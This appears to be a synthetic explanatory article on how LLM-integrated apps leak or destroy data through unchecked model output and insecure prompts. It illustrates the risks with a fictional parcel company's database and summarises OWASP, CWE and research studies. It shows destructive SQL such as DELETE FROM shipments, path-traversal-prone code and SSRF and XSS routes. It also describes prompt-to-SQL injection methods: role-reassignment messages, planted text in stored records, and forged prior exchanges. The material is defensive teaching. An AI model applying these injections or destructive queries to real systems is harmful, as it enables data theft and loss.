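# Insecure output handling and insecure prompts: how applications built on language models lose or leak data

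## How an application connects a language model to a database

A large language model (LLM) is a program that learns patterns from a very large body of text and uses them to generate text in reply to its input. Many companies now build these models into their own software, such as an assistant on a support page, a tool that turns a manager's plain-English question into sales figures, or a coding helper that proposes commands for a developer's machine. An LLM-integrated application is software that sends text to an LLM and uses the reply in its own operation. The prompt is all the text the model receives, usually the developer's instructions, the user's request and any data the application has retrieved.

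Applications built on language models can lose or leak data through two related weaknesses. Insecure output handling means passing the model's output to another component, such as a database or a browser, without adequate checks. An insecure prompt mixes untrusted text with instructions, or relies on instructions alone to enforce a security rule. Either weakness can cause a record to be deleted or let one customer read another's address. The cause can be an attacker's crafted input or a mistake by the model.

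Both weaknesses lie in the connections between an application's parts. A small fictional delivery company, Tern Parcel, can illustrate them. Its customers log in to a website, where a support assistant built on a language model answers their questions using a database.

### The table, the commands and the credential

Tern keeps its deliveries in a table called `shipments`. Three of its rows look like this:

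| id | customer_id | address | status | delivery_note |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1041 | 77 | 3 Mill Lane | delivered | Leave with neighbour |
| 1042 | 58 | 19 Harbour Road | in transit | Ring twice, bell is faint |
| 1043 | 91 | 8 Station Street | at depot | |

PostgreSQL's *Concepts*, part of the manual for a widely used database system, defines a table as a named collection of rows. Here each row records one shipment, and each column holds one kind of fact about it. Tern's staff and systems fill in most of the columns, but whoever books a shipment can type anything into the last one, `delivery_note`.

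Programs read and change such tables by sending commands in SQL, a language made for the purpose. People commonly call any such command a query, even when it changes something. Three kinds matter here:

```sql
SELECT address FROM shipments WHERE id = 1041;
UPDATE shipments SET status = 'delivered' WHERE id = 1041;
DELETE FROM shipments WHERE id = 1041;
```

`SELECT` reads data without changing it, `UPDATE` changes values in existing rows, and `DELETE` removes whole rows. The `WHERE` clause specifies which rows a query applies to. A `DELETE` with no `WHERE` clause is a valid query that empties the entire table, and PostgreSQL's *Deletions* warns that the system will not ask for confirmation first.

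Before the database accepts any query, the application has to log in, typically with a user name and password. This is its database credential. It belongs to an account, which PostgreSQL calls a role, and the role carries a list of permitted operations. According to PostgreSQL's *Privileges*, reading, inserting, updating and deleting are separate privileges, and an administrator hands them out table by table. If Tern wanted its assistant only to read, one line would do it:

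```sql
GRANT SELECT ON shipments TO support_assistant;
```

The database would then refuse a `DELETE` from that role, no matter who or what wrote it. PostgreSQL can also narrow the grant by limiting `SELECT` to named columns. However, the role that creates a table normally owns it, and the right to alter or drop the table comes with ownership and cannot be revoked separately. If a developer lets the assistant log in with the account that set up the database, the assistant can therefore drop `shipments`.

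In *Words Become SQL*, Pedro, Coimbra and colleagues (2025) observe that assistants that query databases often hold broad credentials, so a single generated query can have an outsized effect. They add that many applications reuse similar templates and tools, so the same misconfiguration recurs.

### One question, from browser to answer

Customer 58 is logged in and types "Where is shipment 1042?" Her browser sends the sentence to Tern's application, the program running on the company's server. The application does not pass the sentence to the model by itself. It first inserts it into a prompt template, a form that the developer wrote in advance with blanks for the parts that vary:

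```
You help customers of a parcel company.
Write one PostgreSQL query that finds the answer
to the question below.
Available tables: {table_info}
Question: {input}
```

The application replaces `{table_info}` with the name and columns of `shipments`, and `{input}` with the customer's sentence. What reaches the model is one continuous piece of text, part of it written by Tern's developer and part by a customer. The model replies with more text:

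```sql
SELECT status, delivery_note FROM shipments WHERE id = 1042;
```

So far the reply is only text, and it would have no effect on the database if the application just displayed or discarded it. Tern's application instead extracts the query from the reply and sends it to the database using the application's own credential. The database runs the query and returns a status, "in transit", and a note about a faint bell.

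The application calls the model a second time to turn the two returned values into a reply the customer can easily understand. This second prompt contains the question, the query, the values and an instruction to write the reply. The model produces something like "Shipment 1042 is in transit. The driver has a note to ring twice." The application sends this text to the browser, which displays it.

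Pedro and colleagues describe the same three stages (generating the query, executing it, wording the answer) in applications built on LangChain, a popular library of ready-made parts for connecting models to other software. LangChain picks the SQL out of the model's reply, runs it, appends the result to the prompt and has the model complete the remaining field. The model does not operate the database itself, although the template they reproduce has instructions for it to create a query and then look at the results.

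The query from customer 58's request also has no condition on `customer_id`. This does no harm here because shipment 1042 is hers. If she had typed 1041, the same template could have produced the same query with that number, and no step described so far would have stopped the database from returning another customer's row.

### Two designs: a whole query or a few arguments

Tern's assistant uses the first of two common designs, in which the model writes the entire SQL query. LangChain's *Build a SQL agent* shows how much text can pass back and forth for a single question. The tutorial asks which genre in a digital media store's sample database has the longest tracks on average. The model requests a list of tables, then the structure of two of them, then a check of its draft query, then the execution of that query, and finally writes the answer. That takes five replies from the model, plus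 a sixth call to the model within the checking step. LangChain distinguishes this kind of agent, which can query the database as many times as the question requires, from a chain, which goes through a fixed set of stages once.

When the tutorial's code fetches a table's structure, it also fetches three sample rows and puts them in the prompt. With Tern's `shipments` table, that would show the model three customers' addresses and delivery notes before it had written any query. The checking step has the model look for eight common mistakes, such as wrong data types or badly quoted names, but not consider whether the query should run at all. The prompt forbids commands that change data, but the function that executes queries passes any string it receives to the database without inspecting it. LangChain's tutorial labels its database functions as demonstrations unfit for production and advises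 developers to add validation and scope permissions as narrowly as possible. These measures reduce the risk but don't eliminate it.

In the second design the developer writes the query in advance, inside a function, and the model only fills in the function's arguments. OpenAI's *Function calling* lays out the sequence. The application sends the model a prompt together with a list of available functions, each with a name, a description and a specification of its arguments. The model may answer with a tool call, which is structured output that names a function and supplies its arguments. The application runs the function, sends the result back in a second request, and receives either a final answer or further tool calls. For the question about shipment 1042, the tool call might look like this, with the three fields that Anthropic's *Handle tool calls* lists for that company's models:

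```json
{
  "id": "call_01",
  "name": "get_shipment_status",
  "input": { "shipment_id": 1042 }
}
```

The `id` lets the application match the result to the call later. Behind the function's name stands a query that Tern's developer wrote:

```sql
SELECT status, delivery_note FROM shipments
WHERE id = $1 AND customer_id = $2;
```

This is a parameterised query. `$1` and `$2` are placeholders, and the application sends their values separately from the command, so the database treats them as data and never as SQL. The first value, 1042, comes from the tool call. The second, 58, comes from the customer's login, not from the model. As a general rule, OpenAI's guide advises developers not to make the model fill in an argument that the code already has. The guide presents this as a way to reduce the model's work, but it also improves security, because no wording in the prompt can change a value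 that the model does not supply.

Designs for connecting a model to a database differ in how much of the final command the model composes. Using tool calls does not by itself make a design safe. LangChain's agent uses them, but one of its functions takes a complete SQL query as its only argument. A fixed function can also be dangerous if, for example, it is named `delete_shipment` and accepts any number.

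The first design can answer questions that its developers didn't foresee. Tern's manager could ask which streets had the most failed deliveries in March without anyone having written a function for that question. However, in Microsoft's *Considering NL2SQL?* (2026), Jerry Nixon, a program manager at the company, points out that a model may write a different query each time it receives the same question, so developers can test examples but not every query the model might produce. He would limit generated SQL to development work and open-ended exploration of data. For business systems in live use, he recommends a constrained request, in which the model names a table, some columns and a filter, and ordinary code builds a parameterised query from them. Nixon is introducing a Microsoft product that works this way, so he has an interest in the conclusion, but his point about testing still holds.

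### Where untrusted text enters and where text becomes action

Under either design, the model produces text and other software acts on it. Anthropic's *How tool use works* states, "The model never runs anything on its own." The model emits a structured request, and code outside the model carries it out. That code usually belongs to the application's developer, but for a few functions, such as web search, it runs on Anthropic's servers. The model receives only descriptions of the developer's functions and the results they return, not their code.

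In security engineering, a sink is a component that acts on the text it receives, such as Tern's database. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) lists other sinks that model output commonly reaches, including command-execution tools, the template engines that assemble web pages, and browsers, which may run code in the pages they display. According to the paper, the model usually gives an outsider a way to influence a component that was already unsafe to feed unchecked text, rather than creating the underlying flaw.

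A trust boundary is a place where data crosses between parts of a system that deserve different degrees of trust. Microsoft's *Trust boundary*, a guide to marking these boundaries on diagrams, gives firewalls and connections to outside services as examples. The idea is older than language models. Adam Shostack searched his bookshelf for its origin and reported on the blog Shostack + Friends that he found a well-formed definition in the 2003 edition of Howard and LeBlanc's *Writing Secure Code*, but no mention of the term in the 2002 edition.

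On Tern's path, with the model writing the whole query, the crossings fall as follows:

| Step | Text that moves | Who can influence it | What happens there |
|---|---|---|---|
| Browser to application | The question | Any customer | Untrusted text enters |
| Application to model | Template, table description, question | The developer and the customer | Trusted and untrusted text merge |
| Model to application | The SQL query | Anyone whose text was in the prompt | The output needs checking |
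| Application to database | The same query | As above | Text becomes action |
| Database to model, through the application | Status and delivery note | Whoever booked the shipment | Untrusted text enters again |
| Model to browser, through the application | The worded answer | Anyone whose text was in either prompt | The browser acts as a second sink |

The third row is the easiest for developers to overlook, because the model's reply comes from a service that the company chose and pays for, and it looks like the output of Tern's own software. But a customer's sentence helped shape that reply, and some sentences can make a model depart from its developer's instructions, which is known as prompt injection. The query therefore deserves no more trust than the least trustworthy text in the prompt. The fifth row is even less obvious, because the delivery note comes from Tern's own database, but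 a stranger may have typed it weeks earlier.

The danger of a model's reply depends on what the application does with it at the fourth step. Natanzi and Tang (2026), in *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities*, note that the same string can be harmless in an isolated chatbot and dangerous in a system that is allowed to write to a database. If a model with no connections replies with `DELETE FROM shipments WHERE id = 1042;`, the customer sees an odd line of text. If Tern's application receives the same reply, it extracts the query and sends it to the database, as it did with the `SELECT`, and the database deletes the row if the credential permits deletion.

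## Insecure output handling

If the model writes a `DELETE` and Tern's application runs it without inspecting it, the fault lies in the application. This fault is usually called improper output handling, a name that comes from OWASP (the Open Worldwide Application Security Project), a non-profit foundation that publishes ranked lists of software risks. OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* defines it as insufficient "validation, sanitization, and handling" of a model's output before it passes to other components. Validation checks that the output has an allowed form and requests an allowed kind of operation. Sanitisation removes or neutralises parts that a sink would wrongly act on.

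Users can influence a model's output through the prompt, so OWASP compares passing that output on unchecked to giving users indirect access to whatever the next component can do. Customer 58 has no account on Tern's database, but she can make some use of the assistant's account through the assistant. Tern's application has this flaw from the day it goes live, even if nobody exploits it.

OWASP's first list for language models, in 2023, included the flaw as "insecure output handling". *LLM02*, the 2023 entry, defines it almost as the 2025 entry does, but its common examples cover only command shells and browsers. The 2025 entry adds examples involving SQL queries, file paths and email templates.

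The second standard definition comes from the Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE), the non-profit organisation MITRE's public catalogue of the mistakes that cause vulnerabilities. *CWE-1426* describes a product that uses a generative AI component and does not sufficiently check its outputs against "the intended security, content, or privacy policy". This is broader than OWASP's definition in that it includes breaches of content policy, such as a chatbot insulting a customer in plain text, even when no sink has done anything harmful. It is also narrower, because it concerns only validation. Failing to encode output so that a browser displays it as text is a separate entry, CWE-116.

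MITRE discourages analysts from using CWE-1426 to label real vulnerabilities. A working group wrote the entry in June and July 2024 and chose to publish it quickly and improve it later. MITRE warns that analysts might apply it to anything involving prompt injection and miss the root cause. It recommends older entries where they fit, such as CWE-94 (code injection) when output goes straight into a component that executes code. Few people have used CWE-1426. GCVE's *Improper Validation of Generative AI Output*, a page in a public vulnerability database, lists three vulnerabilities under it, including one in GitHub Copilot and Visual Studio Code and one in the workplace chat product Mattermost, whose AI plugin did not restrict which internet domains the model could request to contact.

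### Overreliance, prompt injection and excessive agency

OWASP separates insecure output handling from overreliance, the broader problem of depending too much on a model's answers being right. One of its scenarios could be either, depending on whether a person or a program acts on the model's mistake. In that scenario, a model that helps write software recommends a package that does not exist, and a developer downloads malware as a result. This is overreliance if the developer read the recommendation and installed the package by hand. It is insecure output handling if a coding agent ran the installation command by itself, because the application then passed unchecked output to a shell.

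Prompt injection is an attack on an application, whereas insecure output handling is a weakness in it, and either can occur without the other. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recount a 2025 report about a public order-tracking chatbot that took an order number from a user's message and looked it up without checking who owned the order. It gave out other customers' email addresses and shipping details, and the order numbers followed a pattern that anyone could guess. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian label the requests as prompt injection, but the user only asked for the contact information on an order, and the model extracted the number and passed it on, as the developer had built it to do. On that account, the application had insecure output handling, and nobody needed to make the model depart from its instructions. Conversely, a customer who talks Tern's assistant into writing poetry has carried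 out a prompt injection, but if the website displays the poem as plain text, no sink acts on it.

Excessive agency is harder to separate from insecure output handling because one incident can involve both. In another of OWASP's scenarios, a chatbot passes its replies to an extension that also offers administrative functions meant for a different, privileged model. One unchecked reply causes the extension to shut down for maintenance. OWASP classifies this as an output handling fault, but the chatbot also had access to functions it did not need. Either removing those functions or checking the reply would have prevented the shutdown. An application that needs a dangerous permission can have insecure output handling without excessive agency. If Tern wants its assistant to cancel bookings, the right to delete rows is not excessive, so safety depends on checking each deletion.

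### What each sink does with the text

A SQL engine runs any valid query that the application's credential permits, so a query written by the model can disclose, falsify or delete records. The user does not need to know SQL, because the model translates ordinary sentences into it. In an OWASP example, a user asks a chat feature for a query that deletes every table, and the application runs the query without checking it.

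A **command shell** runs operating-system commands. It treats certain punctuation marks as separators between commands, so text that a developer intended as a file name can carry an extra command. Functions such as Python's `eval` are similar but run a string as program code. Injected commands or code can reach everything the application's operating-system account can, which may include backups and the file that holds the database password. *VIPER-MCP* (Sun, Kang and colleagues, 2026) reports such a flaw in bytebot, an open-source agent that operates a desktop computer. Bytebot's file-writing function inserted a path supplied by the model into a shell command that ran with administrator rights. A crafted path could give an attacker full control of the container, the isolated environment in which the agent runs.

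Model output can be dangerous in a browser because the browser runs scripts in a page as though the website's owner had written them. Planting such a script is called cross-site scripting, or XSS. The script can read whatever the page can read, often including the token that keeps a user logged in. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a 2024 demonstration by Johann Rehberger against DeepSeek's chat interface. The user's message contained an encoded script, the model decoded it, and the interface inserted the result into the page as code for the browser to run. If Tern saved such a reply in a support ticket, the script could run later in the browser of the employee who opened it. Even without a script, a browser can send data out by loading an image whose address contains the data.

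**Template engines** assemble web pages and emails by filling in blanks, and many also evaluate small expressions marked off by special characters. Tern could safely pass the model's reply to an engine as the value for a blank, but if it passed the reply as the template itself, the engine would evaluate any expression in the reply. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian cite an agent application that did this with Jinja2, a widely used engine for Python. An expression in that application could run operating system commands, so the possible harm was the same as with a shell.

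A **file path** is an instruction about where to read or write. Suppose Tern stores shipping labels as files and opens them like this:

```python
open("labels/" + name_from_model)
```

The developer expects a name such as `1042.pdf`, but operating systems also accept names that step upwards out of a folder, so a different string could open Tern's configuration file. Depending on the function that uses the path, the application might disclose, overwrite or delete the wrong file. This flaw is called path traversal. Sun and colleagues found it in a program called lanhu-mcp. A function for managing project messages extracted a project number from a web address and built a file path from it without checking that it was a number.

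A **server-side web request** fetches an address from inside the company's network. An outsider who can choose the address may reach internal services that refuse connections from the internet, an attack called server-side request forgery (SSRF). To test it, Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built TicketOracle, a deliberately vulnerable concert-ticket application whose assistant could fetch any address the model supplied. An administrative service on the same machine accepted only local requests, and requesting one of its addresses deleted users. In April 2026 they gave seven models ten messages each that pushed them to fetch such an address. Five models complied every time, while GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.6 never did. The ten attempts on each model took place within one conversation, so they are not independent. The application was the same in every test, and the choice of model affected only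 how likely the attack was to work.

### Old flaws with a new route to them

All six sinks were dangerous before language models existed, which supports Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian's argument that the model rarely creates the underlying flaw. They cite public cases for SQL, browser scripts, templates, shell commands and access to other people's records. For three other kinds of attack, including SSRF, they made up scenarios by analogy, and they tested only SSRF.

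In one of their public cases, a program called aws-mcp-server let coding assistants run commands for Amazon's cloud services but did not safely separate those commands from other shell commands, which is an ordinary command injection flaw. Such programs often run on a developer's own machine, where an outside attacker cannot contact them. However, the attacker could plant text in a file in a shared code repository. When the developer's assistant read the file, the text could lead the model to add an extra command to its next tool call.

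MITRE makes a similar comparison with second-order SQL injection, an older attack in which someone stores harmful text in a database and another part of the program later builds a query from it without checking it. In both cases the harmful text reaches the vulnerable component indirectly.

Shifat, Baburaj and colleagues (2026), in *LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild*, provide a broader test of the argument. They collected 295 security advisories that mentioned language-model components and that GitHub, the largest host of open-source code, published between January 2025 and January 2026. An advisory usually labels a flaw with one or more CWE numbers. The ten most frequent were:

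| Weakness | CWE number | Occurrences |
|---|---|---|
| Code injection | 94 | 24 |
| Unsafe deserialisation (rebuilding program objects from untrusted data) | 502 | 22 |
| Command injection | 77 | 22 |
| Operating-system command injection | 78 | 19 |
| Cross-site scripting | 79 | 19 |
| Path traversal | 22 | 18 |
| Inefficient regular expressions | 1333 | 14 |
| Allocating resources without limits | 770 | 12 |
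| Uncontrolled resource consumption | 400 | 11 |
| SQL injection | 89 | 11 |

All ten are familiar from conventional software, and Shifat and colleagues found no implementation weakness specific to language models. This supports the argument, but less strongly than it first appears, because the labels come from an existing catalogue whose entry for unvalidated model output has a warning against its use. A new kind of flaw would therefore probably have received an old label.

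Many of the advisories also have nothing to do with model output. Two of the researchers read a random sample of 100 and sorted them by OWASP's 2025 categories, allowing more than one category for each. Supply-chain risk applied to 44 and improper output handling to 12. Of those 12, ten also involved prompt injection, eight involved excessive agency, and seven involved both. Shifat and colleagues conclude that CWE numbers describe the defect in the code but not how an attacker reaches it.

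Some cases don't fit the argument well. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian discuss an attack on an assistant's long-term memory, in which a malicious web page makes a logged-in user's browser send a forged request that stores a false fact. Forging requests is an old technique, but the harm comes later, perhaps in an unrelated conversation, when the model retrieves the false fact and uses it to answer a question, such as where to send a payment. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian also leave out applications that execute code written by the model, because these fall outside traditional web vulnerabilities.

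Tern's first design, in which the model writes the whole query, is also hard to classify. In classic SQL injection, the developer writes a query with a fixed purpose and a user's input changes its structure. Tern's developer set no structure, and the application is meant to run queries that the model writes. Placeholders cannot fix this, because the model supplies the command as well as the values.

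According to *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (2026), another difference is that the model can generate the harmful string, whereas in an ordinary web attack the attacker submits it. A filter on the customer's message might therefore find nothing to block, as with the encoded script in the DeepSeek demonstration. The model can also write a harmful query by mistake, with no attacker involved. The argument is right about where most of the repairs belong, since the sinks and their defences are old, but that does not mean developers can keep checking only what users type.

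### How often model output can reach a sink

Programmers look for injection flaws with taint analysis, which traces untrusted values through source code to see whether they reach a sink. The trace breaks at a call to a language model, because no code describes how the model turns its input into its output. *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* (Xu, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) reports that established tools such as CodeQL and Semgrep never mark a model's reply as untrusted. A scan of Tern's code with such a tool could therefore miss the path from a customer's question to the database.

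Xu and colleagues developed a method called PRISM to fill this gap. They took Python programs from GitHub that call language models, reconstructed the prompts with plausible values and ran them. This produced 8,119 pairs of a prompt input and the resulting output. In 93% of the pairs, the input left some trace in the output, such as a copied phrase, a summary or a yes-or-no decision. A follow-up study by Xu, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Sightline*, used code from 2,103 families of repositories and found that 12–14% of inputs did not reach the output, because the model ignored them, lacked the context to use them or refused the request. Most of what an application puts into a prompt therefore affects the reply, but does not necessarily control it.

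To find out how often such influence reaches a sink, the PRISM team drew a random 10% of its collection and kept the 62 files that contained at least one dangerous sink. Pairing each prompt input with each sink in the same file gave 353 combinations. For each combination, three reviewers judged whether an attacker who fully controlled the input could get content through the model to the sink. A majority said yes for 110 combinations (31%), spread over 22 of the 62 files. Of these 22 vulnerable files, seven had code injection, seven SQL injection, five command injection, two SSRF and one unsafe deserialisation.

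The input could reach the sink in 7 of 8 combinations when the model produced shell commands and in 52 of 61 when it produced program code, but in none of the 11 when it produced general summaries. Applications that ask a model for commands or code are usually built to run them, which would explain the difference.

These results do not mean that a third of all such applications are vulnerable. The team selected files that contained dangerous sinks, and the reviewers assumed that an attacker controlled the input, which may not be true of a script that only its author uses. Even when the code contains a vulnerable path, it may be hard to exploit. The team tried to reproduce every closed prompt-injection vulnerability in OpenClaw, an open-source personal assistant, using two commercial models. Only six still worked, and the team attributes the failure of the others to the models' safety training.

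VIPER-MCP, the audit that found the bytebot flaw, applied a stricter test. Sun and colleagues examined MCP servers, which are programs that offer functions to language models through a common standard called the Model Context Protocol (MCP). They gathered 39,884 open-source server repositories from GitHub and traced paths in the code from a function's arguments to sensitive operations, or sinks, such as shells, file operations and web requests. When they found such a path, they ran the server with monitors attached to the sinks and gave an AI agent a request in ordinary language, which their system repeatedly revised using the monitors' records. They counted a flaw only if the agent called the right function, the attacker's value reached the sink and a harmful effect followed.

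The audit confirmed 106 previously unknown vulnerabilities, 67 of which had received public identifiers by the time of the paper. That is roughly one for every 376 repositories, far below PRISM's 22 files in 62. However, VIPER-MCP's denominator includes every server repository that the team collected, whether or not it contains a dangerous sink. The audit also counted only vulnerabilities with a working attack, whereas PRISM's reviewers required only a possible path.

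The true number of flaws is almost certainly higher than 106. The audit did not look for SQL injection or code injection, and some servers depend on outside services that were unavailable during automated scanning. It also excluded functions whose purpose is to perform privileged operations, such as running shell commands. A database function that accepts any SQL query would therefore have been left out for two reasons. In a separate test on 130 servers with known flaws, the system missed ten, which Sun and colleagues attribute to kinds of flaw that it does not cover. But 67 of those servers were in the test because the system had found their flaws. If it found all of these again, it missed ten of the other 63, or about 16%.

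The agents sometimes changed the text they received before passing it on. In one server, the agent repeatedly rewrote the punctuation in an argument into a harmless form, and Sun and colleagues' system needed eight rounds to complete the attack. In lanhu-mcp, the agent at first replaced a suspicious value with an ordinary project number, and the attack took five rounds. Such changes make a casual attack less likely to succeed, but developers cannot rely on them as a check.

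### From second place to tenth

OWASP ranked insecure output handling second in its 2023 list of risks for language model applications. The 2025 edition moved it to fifth, and the 2026 edition, published in August, put it tenth and last. Prompt injection, sensitive information disclosure and excessive agency top the new list, according to SC Media.

The 2026 edition also introduced a new method, in which OWASP (2026) says it tested experts' views against thousands of real incidents. According to Invicti, a security vendor, OWASP gathered 7,714 incidents from public vulnerability databases, and 6,639 contained enough information to classify. The ranking was still based mainly on a community vote, with the incident data as a check. Invicti says improper output handling fell furthest on the list, even though OWASP had expanded the entry to cover terminals (the text windows in which programmers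 run commands) and software that automatically fetches addresses found in a reply.

Because the vote carried so much weight, the fall mainly shows that practitioners now consider other risks more pressing, not that the flaw has become rarer. An entry can drop several places because others have risen past it. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* (2026) reports that unbounded consumption, meaning uncontrolled use that exhausts resources or money, rose from tenth place to sixth, and misinformation from ninth to seventh.

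Prompt injection would not have made the top ten on incident data alone, according to Infosecurity Magazine. OWASP says this is because teams work hard to stop such attacks, so fewer successful ones reach public databases. The same could be true of output handling, but this reasoning could be used to explain a low count for almost any risk, so it needs separate evidence.

In Shifat and colleagues' sample of 100 advisories, ten of the 12 output handling cases were also labelled as prompt injection. If analysts assign each incident to a single category, the count for output handling will depend heavily on whether they put these overlapping cases under output handling or prompt injection. Public vulnerability databases also mostly record flaws in software that many organisations share. If Tern's own assistant showed one customer another's address, the company might fix the fault without the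 incident entering such a database.

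## Insecure prompts and prompt injection

People sometimes use "insecure prompt" for an input crafted to cause harm, such as a question to Tern's assistant worded so that the model writes a `DELETE`. The phrase can also mean a weakness in the developer's own prompt, which exists before anyone attacks it. Because the crafted input is already called prompt injection, it is clearer to keep "insecure prompt" for the weakness in the developer's prompt.

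Tern's template mixes untrusted text with instructions, because it puts the customer's question directly after the developer's directions. Suppose the developer tried to prevent deletions by adding a line telling the model to write only `SELECT` queries, but left the code and the database credential unchanged. The template would then also rely on an instruction alone to enforce a security rule.

MITRE's catalogue entry for this weakness, *CWE-1427*, covers products that build prompts from outside data in such a way that the model fails to distinguish users' input from the developer's directions. MITRE allows analysts to label real vulnerabilities with this entry, but not with CWE-1426. It classifies the weakness as a form of command injection and notes that a prompt is effectively a command to the chatbot.

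In MITRE's first example, a program takes two CWE numbers from a user, asks a model to explain the difference, and displays the reply. A user can add another request after the second number, and the model may carry it out too. The program handles its output safely, because it encodes the reply so that a browser will not run it as a script, but its prompt is still insecure. MITRE fixes this with a pattern check that accepts only "CWE-" followed by digits.

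This repair works because the field has a fixed form. Tern could protect a box for shipment numbers in the same way, but not a box for free questions, because any pattern that accepts ordinary English also accepts harmful requests written in it. MITRE rates sanitising user input as highly effective, which is plausible for a CWE number but hard to justify for free text. MITRE also says that a model often cannot distinguish the malicious parts of a prompt from the rest.

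MITRE's second example is a joke-telling agent whose instructions contain a secret token. A user who asks about the token may receive it. The improved version protects the token only with added instructions to refuse such requests, but MITRE considers the risk significantly reduced. MITRE then suggests a redesign that keeps secrets out of the instructions, because a user may be able to extract anything the model receives.

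OWASP's *LLM07:2025 System Prompt Leakage* advises developers not to treat the system prompt, the standing instructions they give a model, as a secret or a security control. Attackers can work out many of its rules by sending messages and watching what the model refuses. OWASP therefore recommends that software outside the model check permissions, in a way that people can audit and that gives the same result every time. If Tern's prompt says that customers may see only their own shipments, whether a customer discovers that rule matters much less than whether something other than the prompt enforces it.

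### Direct and indirect injection

In a direct prompt injection, the attacker types the crafted text into the application. In an indirect one, the attacker puts the text somewhere the application will later read it. OWASP's *LLM01*, an early version of its entry on prompt injection, describes indirect injection as occurring when a model accepts input from external sources that an attacker can control. The source can be a web page or, as with Tern's delivery notes, a column in the company's own database.

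An indirect attacker doesn't need access to the chat, only a field to write in that the application will read when someone else asks a question. For example, a stranger who books a parcel with Tern can put instructions to the model in the `delivery_note` column, which is meant for directions to the door. When the recipient asks days later where her parcel is, the application fetches the note along with the status and puts both into the prompt the model uses to write its answer.

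A filter on the chat box would not help, because the recipient's question is innocent. The application then acts in her session and with its own credential. This makes it a confused deputy, a program with legitimate authority that is tricked into using it for someone who lacks it. An attacker who plants a note is at a disadvantage, because they usually cannot see the model's response and adjust the next message, as someone typing into the chat can.

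How much damage the note can do depends partly on how many queries the application allows for each question. In a chain, the model writes one query, which runs before the model sees any stored data, so the note can distort only the answer. An agent can write another query after reading the note, and that query may change data. MITRE cautions that the root cause of an indirect attack may be that the developer trusted an untrustworthy source, in which case a different CWE entry might fit better.

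### The prompt-to-SQL study

*Words Become SQL* follows earlier work by the same Lisbon researchers, who tested both kinds of attack on databases. They introduced the term prompt-to-SQL injection for prompt injection that makes a model write a harmful database query, which the application then runs. *From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks* (Pedro, Carreira and colleagues, 2023) presented their first results. The final version, *Prompt-to-SQL Injections in LLM-Integrated Web Applications* (Pedro, Coimbra and colleagues, 2025), added tests of existing applications. The models date from 2023 or earlier, so the success rates are out of date, but the methods of attack are still instructive.

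The team built a small job-market website with a chatbot. Its database had a table of users, with their email addresses and phone numbers, and a table of job postings. The chatbot's credential permitted every operation on both tables. The team used LangChain with OpenAI's GPT-3.5, then reproduced the attacks on LlamaIndex, a similar framework. For the 2025 version, they repeated each of seven attacks 20 times.

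| Attack | Route | Rules in the prompt | Success with a chain | Success with an agent |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Delete a whole table | Direct | None against it | 100% | 100% |
| Change a user's record | Direct | None against it | 100% | 100% |
| Copy out the users table | Direct | None against it | 100% | 100% |
| Modify the database | Direct | No changes to data | 100% | 100% |
| Read another user's data | Direct | Only the asker's own data | 100% | 100% |
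| Falsify another user's answer | Indirect | Restricted | 100% | 60% |
| Replace another user's email address | Indirect | Restricted | Not applicable | 100% |

The first three attacks were plain requests, which LangChain's default template did not forbid. For two of them, the attacker did not have to write SQL.

The two direct attacks on a restricted prompt took more effort. A short message telling the model to disregard its instructions did not get past the rule against changing data, but a longer one that also assigned the model a new role did. For the indirect attacks, the researchers planted text in stored records. In the simpler attack, text in a job posting made the chatbot tell other users that there were no jobs. In the other, the planted text made the agent run one query to replace the victim's email address with the attacker's and another to answer the victim's question, so that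 nothing seemed wrong. The attacker could then have taken over the account through a password reset.

The 100% figures measure how reliably a chosen attack works once someone has found it, so they do not mean that any attempt would succeed. Of the 361 attack prompts that the team assembled against the same website, 75 (about one in five) achieved one of the four attacks on restricted prompts, which better indicates the effort involved.

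Pedro and colleagues also tried the restricted-prompt attacks on GPT-4, PaLM 2, Llama 2, Vicuna, Guanaco and Tulu. Guanaco and Tulu could not run an agent reliably enough to be tested as one, and Tulu was also too erratic for one of the chain attacks. The attacks worked in all other cases, although PaLM 2 and Llama 2 changed the victim's email address but then either revealed the attack in the answer or kept repeating the change without answering. The team attributes this to the models' difficulty with complicated instructions rather than to any recognition of the attack. GPT-4 was the hardest to manipulate and needed more elaborate prompts.

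The researchers tested five existing open-source applications that turn questions into database queries. They installed the applications on their own machines and hired two security analysts, who each had up to three hours per application. To train an automated attacker, they selected the successful prompts from their set of 361, along with the failures that closely resembled them, and had a language model reword each one several times. They then fine-tuned Mistral-7B, a small open model, on the result. The automated attacker had up to 40 attempts at each attack.

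With GPT-3.5 or GPT-4 behind the applications, there were 23 combinations of application, model and attack to try:

| Attack | Analysts | Automated attacker |
|---|---|---|
| Direct change to data | 8 of 8 | 6 of 8 |
| Falsified answer through planted text | 9 of 9 | 3 of 9 |
| Several queries through planted text | 5 of 6 | 2 of 6 |
| Total | 22 of 23 | 11 of 23 |

The automated attacker's success rate varied widely by model. Against GPT-3.5, it succeeded in 9 of 11 cases, and the analysts succeeded in 10. Against GPT-4, it succeeded in only 2 of 12, while the analysts succeeded in all 12. A developer who had tested GPT-4 only with the automated tool would have greatly overestimated its safety.

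Two of the applications blocked some attacks by design, regardless of which model they used. Dataherald's code rejected any query that would change data, so the analysts could falsify its answers but not alter its records. Na2SQL ran only one query per question, so planted text could not influence a later query.

### Why the written prohibitions failed

A prohibition in a prompt is part of the model's input and is not passed to the database, so it only makes a harmful query less likely. Withholding the database privilege that a harmful query needs blocks the query.

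An attacker with access to the chat can keep rewording a message, often with hints from the replies, and needs to get past a rule in the prompt only once. Pedro and colleagues found that stricter wording stopped some attacks, but they knew of no way to write a prompt that is provably safe against all inputs. Their four proposed defences instead act on the query or the data, or use a second model to inspect query results.

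One of the direct attacks that Pedro and colleagues describe in *Words Become SQL* exploited the format of LangChain's prompt template, which labels the question, the query, its result and the answer. The attacker's message imitated a completed exchange in this format, in which the assistant had already carried out a forbidden command. The researchers explain that the model tends to stay consistent with the text before it, so when it reached the actual question it repeated the command as a real query, even though the prompt still prohibited it.

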